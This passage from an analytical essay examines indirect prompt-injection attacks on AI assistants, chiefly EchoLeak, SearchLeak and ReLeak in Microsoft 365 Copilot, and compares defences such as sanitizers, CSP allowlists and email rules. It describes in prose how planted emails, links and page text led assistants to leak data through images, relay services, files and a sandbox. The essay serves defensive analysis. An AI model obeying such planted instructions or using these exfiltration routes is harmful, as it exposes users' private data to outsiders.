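or about 63 per cent. The attacker reaches an even chance after 69 attempts. At GPT-6 Sol's indirect score of 97.13 per cent, the same calculation gives an even chance after about 24 attempts and a 95 per cent chance after 100. At 99.99 per cent, 100 attempts succeed only about 1 per cent of the time, so the extra nines are well worth having.

Independence is a strong assumption, and real attempts can depart from it in either direction. If an attacker sends the same email 100 times to the same assistant, and the wording alone determines whether it works, then every attempt has the same result as the first, and the chance of at least one success stays at 1 per cent. In a less extreme and more realistic case, one assistant in 50 gives way half the time because of how it is set up, and the other 49 never do. The average failure rate is still 1 per cent, but an attacker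 who picks one assistant and tries it 100 times has only about a 2 per cent chance of succeeding. Whenever some targets are more vulnerable than others and the attacker stays with one of them, the chance of at least one success is below the 63 per cent expected under independence.

An attacker who learns from failure, however, is more likely to succeed than the formula predicts. The formula gives every attempt the same 1 per cent chance, but an automated attacker changes the text after each refusal and keeps whatever brought it closer to success. DeepMind's search programs worked this way and ended with texts that succeeded in most conversations. Such an attacker might have a 1 per cent chance on the first attempt and a 90 per cent chance on the hundredth, and a 99 per cent score from a fixed set of attacks wouldn't reveal this.

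If each of a million emails has a 1 per cent chance of causing a leak, the expected number of leaks is 10,000, whether or not the attempts are independent. Dependence affects only how the leaks are distributed, for example whether they come steadily or all at once when somebody finds a text that works on everyone. Although an individual user may reasonably be satisfied with a model that resists 99 per cent of attacks, a company that serves millions of users can't be, which is why Willison calls 99 per cent a failing grade in security.

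### Two experiments on where a defence sits

If some attacks still succeed after training, a developer needs to know which other layer can best catch them. In *Silent Egress* (2026), Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay compared several layers in one small system. They built an assistant that could open web pages and make network requests, and gave it some secret data. In every run, the user asked it to summarise a page that had an instruction planted in text the assistant loaded automatically, such as the title or the description meant for search engines. A server they controlled recorded whether it received the secret data.

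It arrived in about 89 per cent of 480 runs. In 95 per cent of the successful attacks, checks on the assistant's output detected nothing, because the secret left through a tool and the reply was an ordinary summary. Lan and colleagues, like Singh and colleagues, classify the problem as Hardy's confused deputy.

The researchers then tried different defences. Warnings or instructions that a developer adds to the prompt gave limited protection. Controls on the system and the network, including an allowlist of sites and a check on redirects, did considerably better. Inspecting requests one at a time was less reliable. When the attack spread the secret over several requests, the measured leakage in any single request fell by 73 per cent, and simple tools for detecting private data missed the leak.

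The 89 per cent figure is little evidence of how the leading models of 2026 would behave. Lan and colleagues tested only the seven-billion-parameter version of Qwen2.5, which is small enough to run on a personal computer. They placed the secret directly in the model's input and gave it uncleaned web text. They also used simple, explicit instructions, which a well-trained model would be far more likely to refuse. Defences that rely on the model's judgement were bound to look poor when tested on such a weak model.

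The advantage of the network controls is easier to generalise, because an allowlist treats a request the same way whether it comes from a strong model or a weak one. But part of that advantage came from testing the case that allowlists handle best, where the attacker's server is not on the list. If the attacker had been able to use a relay on a permitted site, as happened with Bard in 2023, the allowlist might have done no better than the prompt.

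In a larger project, Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues (2025) tested AI-Q, a commercial research assistant from the chip company NVIDIA that gathers material and writes reports. Their paper, *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems*, describes how the team, from NVIDIA and the security company Lakera, inserted hostile content at chosen points in the assistant's workflow and scored the system at successive stages. One of the tests used injected Markdown, the notation behind the image leaks of 2023.

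A developer learns more from scores at several stages than from a single score at the end. Planted text may enter with a web page, survive into the assistant's notes and reach the finished report, where a renderer would act on it. Or a step such as summarising may happen to drop it. A developer who checks only the final report can't tell a lucky omission from a working defence, and a later change to the summarising step could bring the leak back.

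Ghosh and colleagues say their tests uncovered new risks, which they reduced with defences suited to each. They published records of 10,796 runs, including the inputs, outputs and tool calls. The security part includes 2,596 attacks on the system without defences and 2,600 with them, so other researchers can compare the two. The developers were testing their own product, and a workflow with different steps might pass on different attacks. Their main argument, which doesn't depend on the particular scores, is that a model that passed its tests in isolation can still cause harm once it is connected to tools, memory and other models, so developers have to test the whole system again.

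### Why Google wanted a sanitizer as well

Google followed this reasoning with Gemini. In June 2025, a month after DeepMind's paper, Google's security team described the layers it had built around the model. One is a Markdown sanitizer, which stops the program from displaying images with outside addresses. The team said that EchoLeak, a zero-click leak that researchers had just disclosed in Microsoft 365 Copilot, would therefore not work on Gemini. Other layers screen incoming material with classifiers (as Microsoft also does), remove suspicious links, and prompt the user to confirm certain actions.

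The sanitizer applies a fixed rule, which makes up for the main weakness of training. If an attack succeeds and the model writes an image with a passport number in its address, the image still doesn't load, however many times the attacker has practised. Google's engineers can also fix a flaw in the sanitizer without retraining Gemini. But they have to decide what counts as an outside address. The Bard leak showed that this is harder than it sounds for a company that runs as many services as Google.

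But the sanitizer would have made no difference in any of the tests that Shi and colleagues reported, because those attacks sent data through Gemini's email and calendar functions, not through images. Users sometimes want Gemini to email a stranger, so Google can't simply block such emails. It can ask the user to confirm each one, which works if the user reads the request carefully. A model trained to recognise planted instructions may stop the attack before the user has to be asked. This is why Shi and colleagues recommend defences at every layer, from the model's recognition of an attack down to the hardware it runs on.

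Training also covers harms in which no data leaves. A sentence planted in a web page might make an assistant recommend a worthless product or leave an important warning out of a summary. A CSP, an allowlist and a sanitizer could all work perfectly while the user read something false, because the answer would contain no address and the browser would have no request to refuse. Network rules alone can give a firm guarantee against one kind of data theft, but they can't protect users from being misled. Detecting misleading answers requires a control that takes account of meaning, which at present means a trained model or a classifier, and neither is certain to catch them.

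Training is therefore the weaker of the two controls against image leaks, and Google was right not to depend on it. Training is still useful against misleading answers, where there is no fixed rule to use instead, because a model that resists 97 attacks in 100 is much better than one that fails against most of them.

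## Filtering the output: EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Microsoft 365 Copilot also had an output filter, but in January 2025 researchers at Aim Labs, part of the security company Aim Security, found a way to get private data past it. Copilot answers a question by searching the email, files, internal sites and chats that the user can open, then passing the relevant parts to a language model. An outsider could send an employee an email and later receive data from those sources, even if the employee never opened the email or clicked on anything. The leak happened when the employee asked Copilot an ordinary question and the search picked up the attacker's email along with the organisation's own documents.

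Aim named the flaw EchoLeak. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes three successive controls in Copilot that should have prevented it: a classifier on incoming text, a filter on links and images in the answer, and a content security policy (CSP) in the browser. Each failed for a different reason. The chatbots of 2023 had mostly leaked data because nobody had restricted images at all.

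### From report to repair

*New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked* (Goldman, 2025) reports that Aim's researchers spent about three months working out how Copilot functioned. They reported the flaw to Microsoft in January. Microsoft attempted a fix in April, found more problems around the flaw in May, and finished the repair that month. Adir Gruss, a cofounder of Aim, considered five months a very long time to resolve a report of this kind. He attributed part of the delay to finding the right teams at Microsoft and explaining the problem to them. Aim published its findings on 11 June.

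Microsoft said the flaw had affected no customers. The public record of the flaw, GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), includes an assessment by the US cybersecurity agency CISA, which also lists no exploitation but notes that attackers could have automated the attack. Copilot runs on Microsoft's servers, so outsiders can do little to check either statement.

Microsoft rated the flaw 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5. Both considered the attack easy to carry out over the network, with no account or user action needed. The scores differ mainly because Microsoft judged that the harm crossed from one security domain into another. Microsoft's view fits the incident better, since the attack used an email from outside the organisation to obtain data from inside it.

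Similar attacks came before EchoLeak. Rehberger had demonstrated a leak from Bing Chat in 2023, and Willison (2025), in a post also titled *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’*, considered Aim's attack an extended version of leaks he had seen in a dozen products. Reddy and Gujral (2025) therefore overstate how new the attack was when they call it, in *EchoLeak*, the first known use of prompt injection to steal data from a production system. Ravia's claim is narrower and easier to defend. He argues that in earlier attacks, the user had to direct the chatbot to the hostile material, or the attacker could take only certain data. Copilot retrieved the hostile email by itself, and the attack could leak anything in the model's input.

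### What each control assumed

The classifier was supposed to stop planted instructions in incoming material before they reached the model. It could catch a hostile email only if the email resembled the hostile examples in its training data, and Aim's email was not similar enough. Ravia blames a shortage of good examples, because planted instructions can come in any language, tone or subject. Classifiers are probabilistic, so some misses are expected, and Microsoft had put two further controls behind this one.

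In 2026, Microsoft added a similar check earlier in the process, when its email security service began scanning incoming mail for planted instructions. The service automatically quarantines messages it identifies with high confidence, and the check is on by default for eligible customers. Wrongly flagging a legitimate email does more harm here than inside Copilot, because the employee loses the email itself and not just Copilot's summary of it.

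The link filter acted on the model's answer. Park (2024), in *Copilot*, described its effect on users a month before Aim's report. Copilot replaced links to outside sites with the words "An external link was removed to protect your privacy", even when the user had asked where to read more. Park found this frustrating but accepted the reason for it, and published a way to make Copilot show the address as unclickable text.

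The filter could work only if it covered every way of writing a link or image. It removed the common form but left less common forms, which are equally valid Markdown, in the answer. Aim first used this gap to produce a link that would have leaked data if the user clicked it. The same gap existed for images, which need no click. Willison credited Microsoft with trying to restrict links to approved internal pages, but concluded that it had forgotten to apply the rule to the lesser-known form.

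The image still had to load, but the CSP at first blocked the browser from contacting Aim's server because the server wasn't on Microsoft's list. Aim's researchers then searched the permitted sites for a relay. They first found one in a Microsoft service that worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation, then found one in Microsoft Teams that required nothing from the victim. The browser sent the image's address to Teams, and Teams contacted the attacker's server.

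Willison describes the Teams function as an open redirect, an address that sends the browser on to another site, while Ravia describes a server that makes the request itself. A browser also applies a CSP to the destination of a redirect, so it could have blocked the request to the other site if the function were a redirect. It has no control over a request that Microsoft's own server makes.

The CSP therefore worked as intended, since the browser loaded images only from permitted sites. The problem was the list of those sites. As Ravia reproduces it, the list had 29 different entries, compared with four in Bing Chat's list in 2023. Eleven of the 29 covered whole families of sites (a later section explains how browsers match them). Fourteen entries appeared twice, which suggests that somebody had joined two lists without removing the duplicates.

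Each site on the list makes Copilot's security depend partly on the team that runs that site. The engineers who built the Teams function had no obvious reason to think about Copilot, and whoever added Teams to the list probably wanted to show pictures stored there. Both decisions were reasonable on their own, like the compiler and its extra permission in Hardy's story. To prevent the leak, someone would have had to check what each permitted site did with an address it received, and check again whenever the site gained a feature.

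### Why the filter and the renderer disagreed

The link filter's design would still be fragile if Microsoft added the link forms it misses, because the filter and the renderer parse the same text by different rules. The Azure filter of 2023 had the same weakness.

The filter is safe only if it detects an outside image in every answer from which the renderer would produce one. EchoLeak used an answer in which the filter missed the image but the renderer produced it. If the filter instead detects an image that the renderer would not produce, nothing leaks, but the filter deletes harmless text.

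Testing can find an answer that breaks this condition but can't prove that none exists. Markdown has several dialects, and a renderer's developers can add support for another in a routine update. The filter's developers then have to notice the change and work out what it allows, because an attacker needs only one form that the filter misses.

Web developers faced this problem long before chatbots. In cross-site scripting, an attacker gets a website to display text that the visitor's browser runs as a program, and many sites tried to stop it by searching the text for dangerous patterns. *Consideration Points Detecting Cross-Site Scripting* (2009) attributes much of these filters' weakness to differences between browsers. Browsers tolerated different kinds of malformed markup, so a filter that worked for one browser could fail for another. *Context-Auditor* (2022) still described pattern-based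 filters as limited and liable to fail against new attacks. It also criticised sanitizers for removing characters without regard to what they do on the page, so they could delete harmless text.

The official record of EchoLeak also classifies the flaw under a general type of weakness, in which a program fails to neutralise special elements in output that another component then reads. This describes the link filter's failure well but leaves out the relay.

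A filter can also fail if the renderer displays text before the filter has finished with it. Park's screenshots show a link forming and then turning into plain text as more of the answer arrives. By Park's account, Copilot sent the user's device the Markdown together with a second version from which it had removed the links. A link that appears for a moment does little harm because hardly anyone could click it in time, but an image could leak data in that moment because the renderer requests the image as soon as it tries to display it. Park shows this happening only with a link, and Aim's attack didn't depend on it. But a filter meant to stop images has to finish with each piece of text before the renderer receives it.

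### Parsing once and keeping a small subset

A developer can avoid the disagreement by having only one program interpret the text. To parse a text is to work out its structure, and every Markdown renderer has to do this before it can draw anything. The safer design puts the filter after this step:

1. The program parses the model's answer once, producing a tree of labelled pieces such as paragraphs, lists, bold phrases, links and images.
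2. It copies the kinds of piece on a short approved list into a new tree, and drops everything else or turns it into plain text.
3. If an approved piece contains an address, the program compares the address with a list of permitted destinations.
4. The renderer draws the screen from the new tree and never receives the model's original text.

After parsing, all images are represented the same way, whichever notation the model used. The filter no longer needs a list of notations, because it acts on the same structure that the renderer will draw, so *F* and *R* can't diverge. Any notation the parser doesn't support stays ordinary text and loads nothing. When developers add a new feature to the parser, such as diagrams, the program won't display it until somebody adds it to the approved list. This follows Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults, since forgetting to update the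 list leads to a missing diagram and a complaint.

The guarantee would be that the page contains no image from an address outside the permitted list, provided that the renderer accepts only the filtered tree. The team that owns the renderer has to maintain that condition. It fails if another part of the program formats the original text again, for example for an email notification or a preview.

It can also fail when one program has to pass the answer to another as text, because the receiving program will parse it again. *Towards More Security in Data Exchange* (2015) addresses this with an "unparser", which generates the output from the tree and encodes each piece of data according to where it will appear, so that the next program reads it as data and not as markup. In a trial on a web page that combined HTML with JavaScript, a testing tool raised some alarms, but these were false, because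 the browser displayed the inserted text without running it. The result is encouraging, but it comes from one small application. The method also requires an accurate description of the language that the receiving program understands, which is hard to write for HTML because its rules change from one part of a page to another.

The choice of subset matters as much as the parsing. Reddy and Gujral also recommend reducing the answer to a safe subset, but their example is "links, emphasis, plain images only". A subset that includes images from outside addresses would leave open the route that EchoLeak used. Parsing once would also not have been enough if the tree filter had used the same list of sites as the CSP, because an address at the Teams relay would have passed both. A stricter program would never load an image from an address that the model wrote. Instead, the model could refer to a stored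 picture by number, and the program would look up the address.

With this restriction, Copilot could still show charts from the organisation's own files, but not a photograph from a supplier's website. That seems a reasonable trade-off for an assistant with access to a whole mailbox. Google made a similar choice with Gemini's sanitizer, although *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) doesn't explain whether the sanitizer works on text or on a parsed tree.

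### Eight defences on paper

Reddy and Gujral wrote the most detailed comparison of defences against EchoLeak. They divide the attack into six parts and match them to eight defences. Among these, prompt partitioning marks outside text so that the model can treat it as information only. Provenance gating makes the assistant use internal sources unless the user asks for others. An output policy gate passes only approved notation. A signed media proxy fetches images only from addresses that the program has approved with a digital signature, and only for a limited time. Egress monitoring checks outgoing content for private data and suspicious addresses.

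In the table, "scope violation" is Ravia's term for cases where instructions from an untrusted source lead the model to use trusted data without the user's consent.

| Defence | Scope violation | Classifier bypass | Link filter bypass | Automatic image fetch | Relay on a permitted site | Zero-click leak |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt partitioning | Stops | Stops | – | – | – | Fails |
| Provenance gating | Stops | – | Stops | – | – | Fails |
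| Output policy gate | Stops | Stops | Stops | Fails | – | Fails |
| List of permitted or banned addresses | – | – | Stops | Fails | Stops | Stops |
| Strict CSP | – | – | – | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| Signed media proxy | – | – | – | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| Human approval of outside content | Stops | Stops | Stops | Stops | – | Stops |
| Egress monitoring | – | – | – | – | – | Fails |

A dash means that the defence doesn't apply to that part of the attack.

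The table records Reddy and Gujral's reasoning about what each defence should do. They call it theoretical, and they write in their limitations section that they did not reproduce the attack or run any experiments. They worked from published accounts about two months after the disclosure. One sentence in the paper says that a tick means full coverage "in our tests", which could mislead readers into taking the table for test results.

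The table lists provenance gating as failing against the zero-click leak, but elsewhere the paper argues that EchoLeak fails by design if an assistant never uses email from unknown outside senders to answer questions about internal projects. The second claim is more convincing, since an email that never reaches the model can't instruct it. The table also lists the output policy gate as failing against automatic image fetches, although the paper recommends that such a gate drop disallowed images. If the gate did this before rendering, there would be no disallowed image to fetch.

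The table's entries for CSPs and address lists are too favourable. Copilot had a CSP, and the relay was on its list of permitted sites. A "strict" CSP or address list stops a relay only if whoever writes it already knows which permitted sites can act as one, and finding those sites is the difficult part. According to the table, human approval stops five of the six parts of the attack, more than any other defence, but that relies on a person reading each request carefully.

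The table is more useful as a list of questions. It divides defences into those that keep hostile text away from private data and those that stop that data from leaving, and it shows that an organisation could invest heavily in one group while neglecting the other. Three of the four defences listed as stopping the zero-click leak restrict network requests. Lan and colleagues reached a similar conclusion by experiment, which is better evidence than the table.

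### Microsoft's account of its defences

In July 2025, a month after Aim's disclosure, Microsoft explained how it defends its products against indirect prompt injection. It tries to prevent injections, detect them and limit their impact. For prevention, it uses carefully written standing instructions and spotlighting. It detects injections with Prompt Shields, a classifier that it trains on known attacks and keeps updating. Microsoft calls all of these prevention and detection methods probabilistic.

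The measures that limit the impact include permissions, user consent and fixed rules that block known ways of sending data out. Microsoft prefers deterministic defences where possible, because they can guarantee that a particular attack will fail. It says nobody yet knows how to detect injected instructions deterministically, so it aims to build systems in which a successful injection does not harm customers. It compares this to protections in ordinary software that stop attackers from using a memory error to break in.

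EchoLeak supports the premise. The classifier missed the email, so Copilot needed other controls that didn't depend on recognising it. One that worked was that Copilot could not send email on its own. Microsoft's product documentation says that a user must start or approve any such action. An attacker who had taken control of the model still couldn't make it email the data out, and had to extract the data through the displayed answer instead.

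On the display route, however, the incident counts against Microsoft's confidence in fixed rules, because the link filter and the CSP both applied such rules and the attack passed both. Once Aim had found a form that the filter ignored and a relay that the CSP permitted, those two controls would let the data through on every attempt, whereas a classifier might have caught some of the emails. A deterministic control behaves consistently, but its rule may not cover the right cases, as Microsoft concedes with the phrase "a particular attack".

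Microsoft's example of a deterministic defence is its response to an image leak that Rehberger reported. Microsoft doesn't name the product, but the example matches his 2023 Bing Chat report. Microsoft says it looks beyond each reported flaw to the general class, including variants. This is partly true, since Copilot had both a CSP and a link filter when Aim examined it. But EchoLeak was another leak through a Markdown image, about nineteen months after the Bing Chat fix, and Copilot's CSP had a list about seven times as long. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) weakens the claim further, because it records another leak in the same product, which a later section covers.

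Microsoft did not mention EchoLeak in its July account, and it has published little about the repair. It changed its own servers, so customers had nothing to install or inspect. Reddy and Gujral report that Copilot now strips embedded images and the less common form of link from outside content. That would make the original email less useful to an attacker, but it wouldn't control what the model writes. A lasting repair would also need a filter that recognises every form of image in the answer, a shorter list of allowed sites, or both.

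The rule for ordinary links changed during the same months. Microsoft told customers that between late March and late May 2025, Copilot Chat would stop removing hyperlinks and instead check a link's reputation when the user clicked it. This addressed Park's complaint, and it protects people from sites already known to be malicious. It is a weaker barrier to data exfiltration than removing links, because a new site may have no bad reputation and the check doesn't look for private text in the address. In its July account, Microsoft mentions blocking "certain untrusted links", which is consistent with the change, but it doesn't specify which links.

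Microsoft's later guidance for developers, *Defend against indirect prompt injection attacks*, discusses the drawbacks more openly. It advises developers to expect some attacks to succeed and to combine both kinds of defence. It also warns that using several layers adds complexity, slows responses, causes false alarms and requires continual coordination between engineering, security and product teams. Gruss's explanation for the five-month repair suggests that this coordination is a serious difficulty even at Microsoft.

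### Keeping outside email away from the model

Gruss argues that controls around the model treat a symptom. He thinks the basic flaw is that agents process trusted and untrusted material together, and that a lasting solution needs a clearer separation between instructions and data. Ravia wants defences aimed specifically at scope violations, arguing that a precise name for one kind of memory error once helped engineers develop a specific protection against it. Willison doubts that the new term "scope violation" is needed, because language models have never been able to take account of where their input came from. He is right that the weakness is old, but the term identifies something a program can check. Copilot can identify which messages came from outside, even if the model can't use that information reliably.

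Aim has given two answers on whether customers could have protected themselves. Ravia writes that, to the best of his knowledge, no administrator's setting could have prevented the attack, but Aim Security's *EchoLeak* page says that organisations can configure Copilot to ignore outside email. Both statements could be true if Microsoft added the setting when it fixed the flaw, and Reddy and Gujral mention reports that its patches introduced such options.

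Office 365 IT Pros' *DLP Prevents Microsoft 365 Copilot from Processing External Email* (2026) describes a rule that stops Copilot from using any email from outside the organisation in its answers. Employees can still read these messages in their inboxes, but Copilot can't find them. The rule checks the sender's domain, the part of an email address after the @ sign, against the organisation's own list, so it doesn't depend on recognising an attack. It also covers messages that arrived before an administrator switched it on.

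This removes one of Willison's three conditions, exposure to untrusted text, for one kind of material, but planted instructions can still arrive in a shared document or web page. Copilot also becomes much less useful to people who work mainly with customers and suppliers, because it can no longer summarise what those contacts wrote. The rule treats sister companies as outsiders even when they have joined their Microsoft accounts into one organisation. Office 365 IT Pros suggests applying it only to likely targets such as executives, whose Copilot can also reach the most sensitive files.

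Microsoft made the rule available for preview in July 2026 and plans its general release for late January 2027. The rule is off by default, so Copilot will keep reading outside email unless an administrator turns it on.

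## Microsoft 365 Copilot in 2026: SearchLeak and ReLeak

After fixing EchoLeak, Microsoft promised "additional defense-in-depth measures" in a statement reproduced in the AI Incident Database. Over the next eighteen months, researchers kept finding ways to get private data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. In October 2025, BeyondMachines (2025) reported a leak through the diagrams that Copilot could draw from the model's text. In May 2026, Microsoft published a record of another flaw of the same general type as EchoLeak. SearchLeak followed in June and ReLeak in December.

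SearchLeak got past a sanitizer that ran too late. A sanitizer on the displayed answer could not have stopped two of ReLeak's three leaks.

### One click on a Microsoft link

*SearchLeak* (2026), by the data security company Varonis, describes an attack on Copilot's enterprise search, which answers questions using a company's email, calendars and files. A link to the search page can include a query, and Copilot ran the query as soon as the page opened. An attacker could write instructions into a link to Microsoft's own website and send it to an employee by email or chat. If the employee clicked it, Copilot searched their mailbox and put what it found into the address of an image.

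In SearchLeak, the click started the search and an automatic fetch sent the data a moment later, whereas clicking a leaking link of the kind found in 2023 sends the data directly. The site's name was genuine, so the employee had little chance of spotting the trick from it. Filters that judge a link by its site were also unlikely to flag it, as The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* points out.

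The attacker's text also took the place of the user's own question, so even a model that perfectly ignored instructions in emails and web pages could have obeyed it. Varonis calls this method parameter-to-prompt injection. Copilot could have put the query in the search box and waited for the employee to press a key before running it, which would have added one keystroke for honest users.

Varonis had already used the same entry method against the consumer version of Copilot in an attack named Reprompt, which Microsoft patched in January 2026. Varonis' researchers were surprised that the method also worked on the enterprise product, which supposedly had more guardrails. According to Varonis' *CoSnitch*, Microsoft learned of another flaw of this kind in the consumer version in December 2025 and patched it on 18 August 2026.

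### A sanitizer that ran too late

A language model writes its answer one token at a time, and a long answer can take ten seconds or more. Most chat programs stream the answer so that the user doesn't have to wait for all of it. They send the text to the screen in small pieces as the model produces it, and redraw the page as the answer grows.

Copilot's sanitizer put the model's output inside a code block, which makes a browser show markup as plain characters instead of acting on it. Inside a code block, an image is just a line of odd-looking text. But Copilot added the code block only after the model had finished, so events happened in this order:

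1. The model began its answer, and Copilot streamed it to the browser.
2. The browser received the markup for an image and requested the image.
3. The model finished the answer.
4. The sanitizer turned the markup into harmless text.

By the fourth step the data had already been sent, and changing the page could not retrieve it. Programmers call this a race condition, meaning that the result depends on which of two processes finishes first. Here the sanitizer had little chance of finishing first because it didn't start until the model had stopped writing.

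Anyone who tested Copilot by looking at the finished page would have concluded that the sanitizer worked, because the failure showed up only in the list of requests the browser had made. A hint had been visible about eighteen months earlier in Park's screenshots, which showed links turning into plain text as the answer arrived.

Running the same sanitizer earlier would not have been enough, because a partly received answer is hard to clean. A program can't compare an address with a list until the whole address has arrived. Unsafe markup may be split between two pieces of the stream, neither of which looks unsafe alone. In Markdown, later characters can also change the meaning of earlier ones. For example, a backtick begins code only if another backtick closes it, so a program that has received only the first can't tell whether the next words are code or live markup. A sanitizer can reread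 everything received so far each time a new piece arrives, but the last few characters will always be uncertain.

### Two ways to clean before rendering

Varonis recommends sanitizing the answer as part of rendering it, which a developer can do in two ways. The first is to hold back markup until it is complete. The program shows ordinary words immediately, but hides characters that might begin an image or a link until the model has finished that item and the program has checked it. The second is to show the text as it arrives, perhaps with bold type and headings, but load no images and enable no links until the sanitizer has processed the complete answer.

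To estimate the delays, suppose the model writes *r* tokens per second, the whole answer has *n* tokens, the markup for an image runs from token *a* to token *b*, and the check takes *c* seconds.

| | Pause in the text | Earliest request for the image |
|---|---|---|
| No control | None | *b*/*r* |
| Hold back markup | (*b* − *a*)/*r* + *c* | *b*/*r* + *c* |
| Nothing active until the end | None | *n*/*r* + *c* |

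In an invented but realistic example, a model writes a 600-token answer at 50 tokens per second, and the markup for an image runs from token 100 to token 160. If the program holds back the markup until it is complete, the text pauses for 1.2 seconds and the browser can request the image after 3.2 seconds, not counting the time for the check. If the program waits for the end of the answer instead, the text never pauses, but the browser can't request the image until 12 seconds have passed, 8.8 seconds later.

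Holding back markup adds little delay. A browser can't request an image until its address is complete, so the image is late only by the time the check takes. The text pauses while the model is writing the address, which users don't need to read. Rehberger guessed that OpenAI chose not to filter ChatGPT's replies on its servers for the sake of speed. If so, it was avoiding a small delay.

This method is hard to make accurate because the program has to recognise every way image markup can begin, so it can fail as Copilot's link filter did in EchoLeak. It also needs a rule for markup that begins but never ends, such as releasing it as plain text after a certain length.

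Waiting until the answer is complete is slower but easier to get right, because a renderer that cannot load anything during streaming doesn't need to recognise images at that stage. The guarantee is also easy to state and test: the page makes no request for anything in the answer until the sanitizer has processed all of it. The sanitizer must still handle the finished answer correctly, and parsing the text once, as described in the previous section, would help. For an assistant with access to a company's mailbox, showing a chart nine seconds late is a minor delay. A shopping assistant could leak less private data, and its users mostly want to see pictures, so it could reasonably hold back markup instead.

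### The relay at Bing

The late sanitizer would not have leaked anything by itself, because Copilot's CSP stopped the browser from contacting the attacker's server. But the policy permitted all of Bing's sites, and one Bing service fetched images for analysis from addresses it received. The browser could therefore send Bing a request that made Bing contact the attacker's server. Microsoft Teams had served as the intermediary in EchoLeak.

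Varonis advises security teams to treat any allowed site that fetches user-supplied URLs as a possible route for leaking data. By that standard, Bing was a poor choice for the allowlist, because search engines fetch content from the rest of the web. Copilot could have loaded its images from a separate site that only stored them.

Varonis stresses that the attack needed all three weaknesses: the query in the link, the late sanitizer and the relay. Fixing any one of them stops the reported attack, so a vendor can truthfully call the flaw fixed while leaving the other two for attackers to use in a different chain. Microsoft described SearchLeak as "fully mitigated" on 4 June, eleven days before Varonis published its account, and recorded no exploitation. Microsoft didn't specify in its record which of the three weaknesses it removed.

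Microsoft called the flaw critical on its own scale but scored it 6.5 out of 10 on the industry's common scale, partly because the victim had to click. According to Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026), the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5 on the assumption that no user action was necessary. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) reports the same two scores. The Next Web found a score of 6.5 from both Microsoft and the database, so the database entry may have been revised.

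SearchLeak scored lower than EchoLeak (6.5 against 9.3) partly because Microsoft classified the harm differently. Both attacks sent a company's internal data to an outsider, but Microsoft judged that only EchoLeak crossed from one security domain into another. If it had judged that SearchLeak did too, the scoring formula would have given SearchLeak 7.4.

### ReLeak's three exits

On 3 December 2026, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) disclosed three more leaks, all zero-click. Simonovich works at Cato AI Labs, the team that found EchoLeak as Aim Labs, before Cato Networks bought its parent company in September 2025.

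All three leaks began as EchoLeak had, with an unread email that Copilot retrieved while answering an ordinary question. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026) notes that the employee did not have to approve any permission. Faisal's *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (2026) reports that Microsoft's protections against planted instructions blocked none of the three. The leaks differed in how the data got out.

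| Exit | Record | Patched (2026) | Severity | Through the display? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Images fetched through Bing | CVE-2026-124115 | 15 November | No confirmed score | Yes |
| Files that Copilot created | CVE-2026-124132 | 11 November | No confirmed score | No |
| Code sandbox | CVE-2026-78501 | 17 September | Critical, 8.6 | No |

Cato reported the flaws between 29 July and 20 August. Microsoft therefore took between four and just over seven weeks to close the sandbox exit, and between twelve and sixteen weeks to close the one through Bing. Both fixes took less time than the one for EchoLeak, which took five months.

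The exit through Bing is the most awkward for Microsoft. *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* (Antipov, 2026) describes it as similar to SearchLeak's channel, except that SearchLeak needed a click. Cato reported the Bing exit within eleven weeks of Microsoft's announcement that SearchLeak was fully mitigated. Whatever Microsoft had repaired in June, Bing could still pass data from a Copilot answer to an outsider until mid-November.

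The second way data could leave was through Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files that Copilot created and saved in OneDrive or SharePoint, Microsoft's file storage services. In Cato's tests, Microsoft's servers sent the data out while processing a file in the background, one to eight minutes after the conversation had ended, without anyone opening the file. An employee who watched the whole conversation closely could still have lost the data after closing the window.

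The third exit was Copilot's code interpreter, which runs short programs in a sandbox, an environment isolated from other systems. Microsoft guaranteed in its documentation that no network traffic could enter or leave the sandbox. The guarantee was well written because it was precise, named the layer responsible, and didn't depend on the content of any text. But Cato's researchers got past the isolation and sent data straight to an outside server. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) draws developers' attention to this failure in particular.

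The fault in Copilot's CSP was in a list that anyone could read, but nobody could have found the sandbox's fault by reading its documentation. Customers who rely on a sandbox like this need evidence that somebody competent has tried to break it. Antipov adds that agents that customers build in two other Microsoft products can also use the code interpreter, though nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected them.

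Microsoft first scored the sandbox flaw at 7.4 and later raised the score to 8.6. Under the scoring formula, a flaw that exposes data across a security boundary scores 7.4 if the victim must do something and 8.6 if not. Microsoft may at first have counted the employee's question to Copilot as an action by the victim. That would be a generous reading, since asking questions is the normal way to use Copilot.

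AI agents helped Cato's researchers by writing test cases, analysing Copilot's refusals and adjusting the next attempt, much as DeepMind's attacking programs did with Gemini. A fixed rule with a gap may survive for years if finding the gap takes months of skilled work, as it did for EchoLeak, but automated searching makes it likely that such gaps will be found sooner.

### The verdict and Microsoft's response

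A year and a half after EchoLeak, Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made". Its researchers said the underlying weakness was that Copilot could not reliably tell untrusted content from legitimate instructions. Microsoft made all the repairs on its own servers and told customers they needed to do nothing. Cato said it knew of no affected customers or real attacks, but it can't inspect Microsoft's logs, so its statement is weaker evidence than a search of those logs would be.

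Cato sells security products, so it has a commercial interest in a pessimistic assessment. The Next Web had been even harsher in June, when it counted three disclosures in six months, each defeating the protections the previous fix was supposed to establish. That count is wrong, because EchoLeak became public a year before SearchLeak, and Reprompt concerned the consumer product. The leak through Bing is much better evidence for Cato's assessment, because it was the third time data had leaked from the same product through an image and a permitted Microsoft service.

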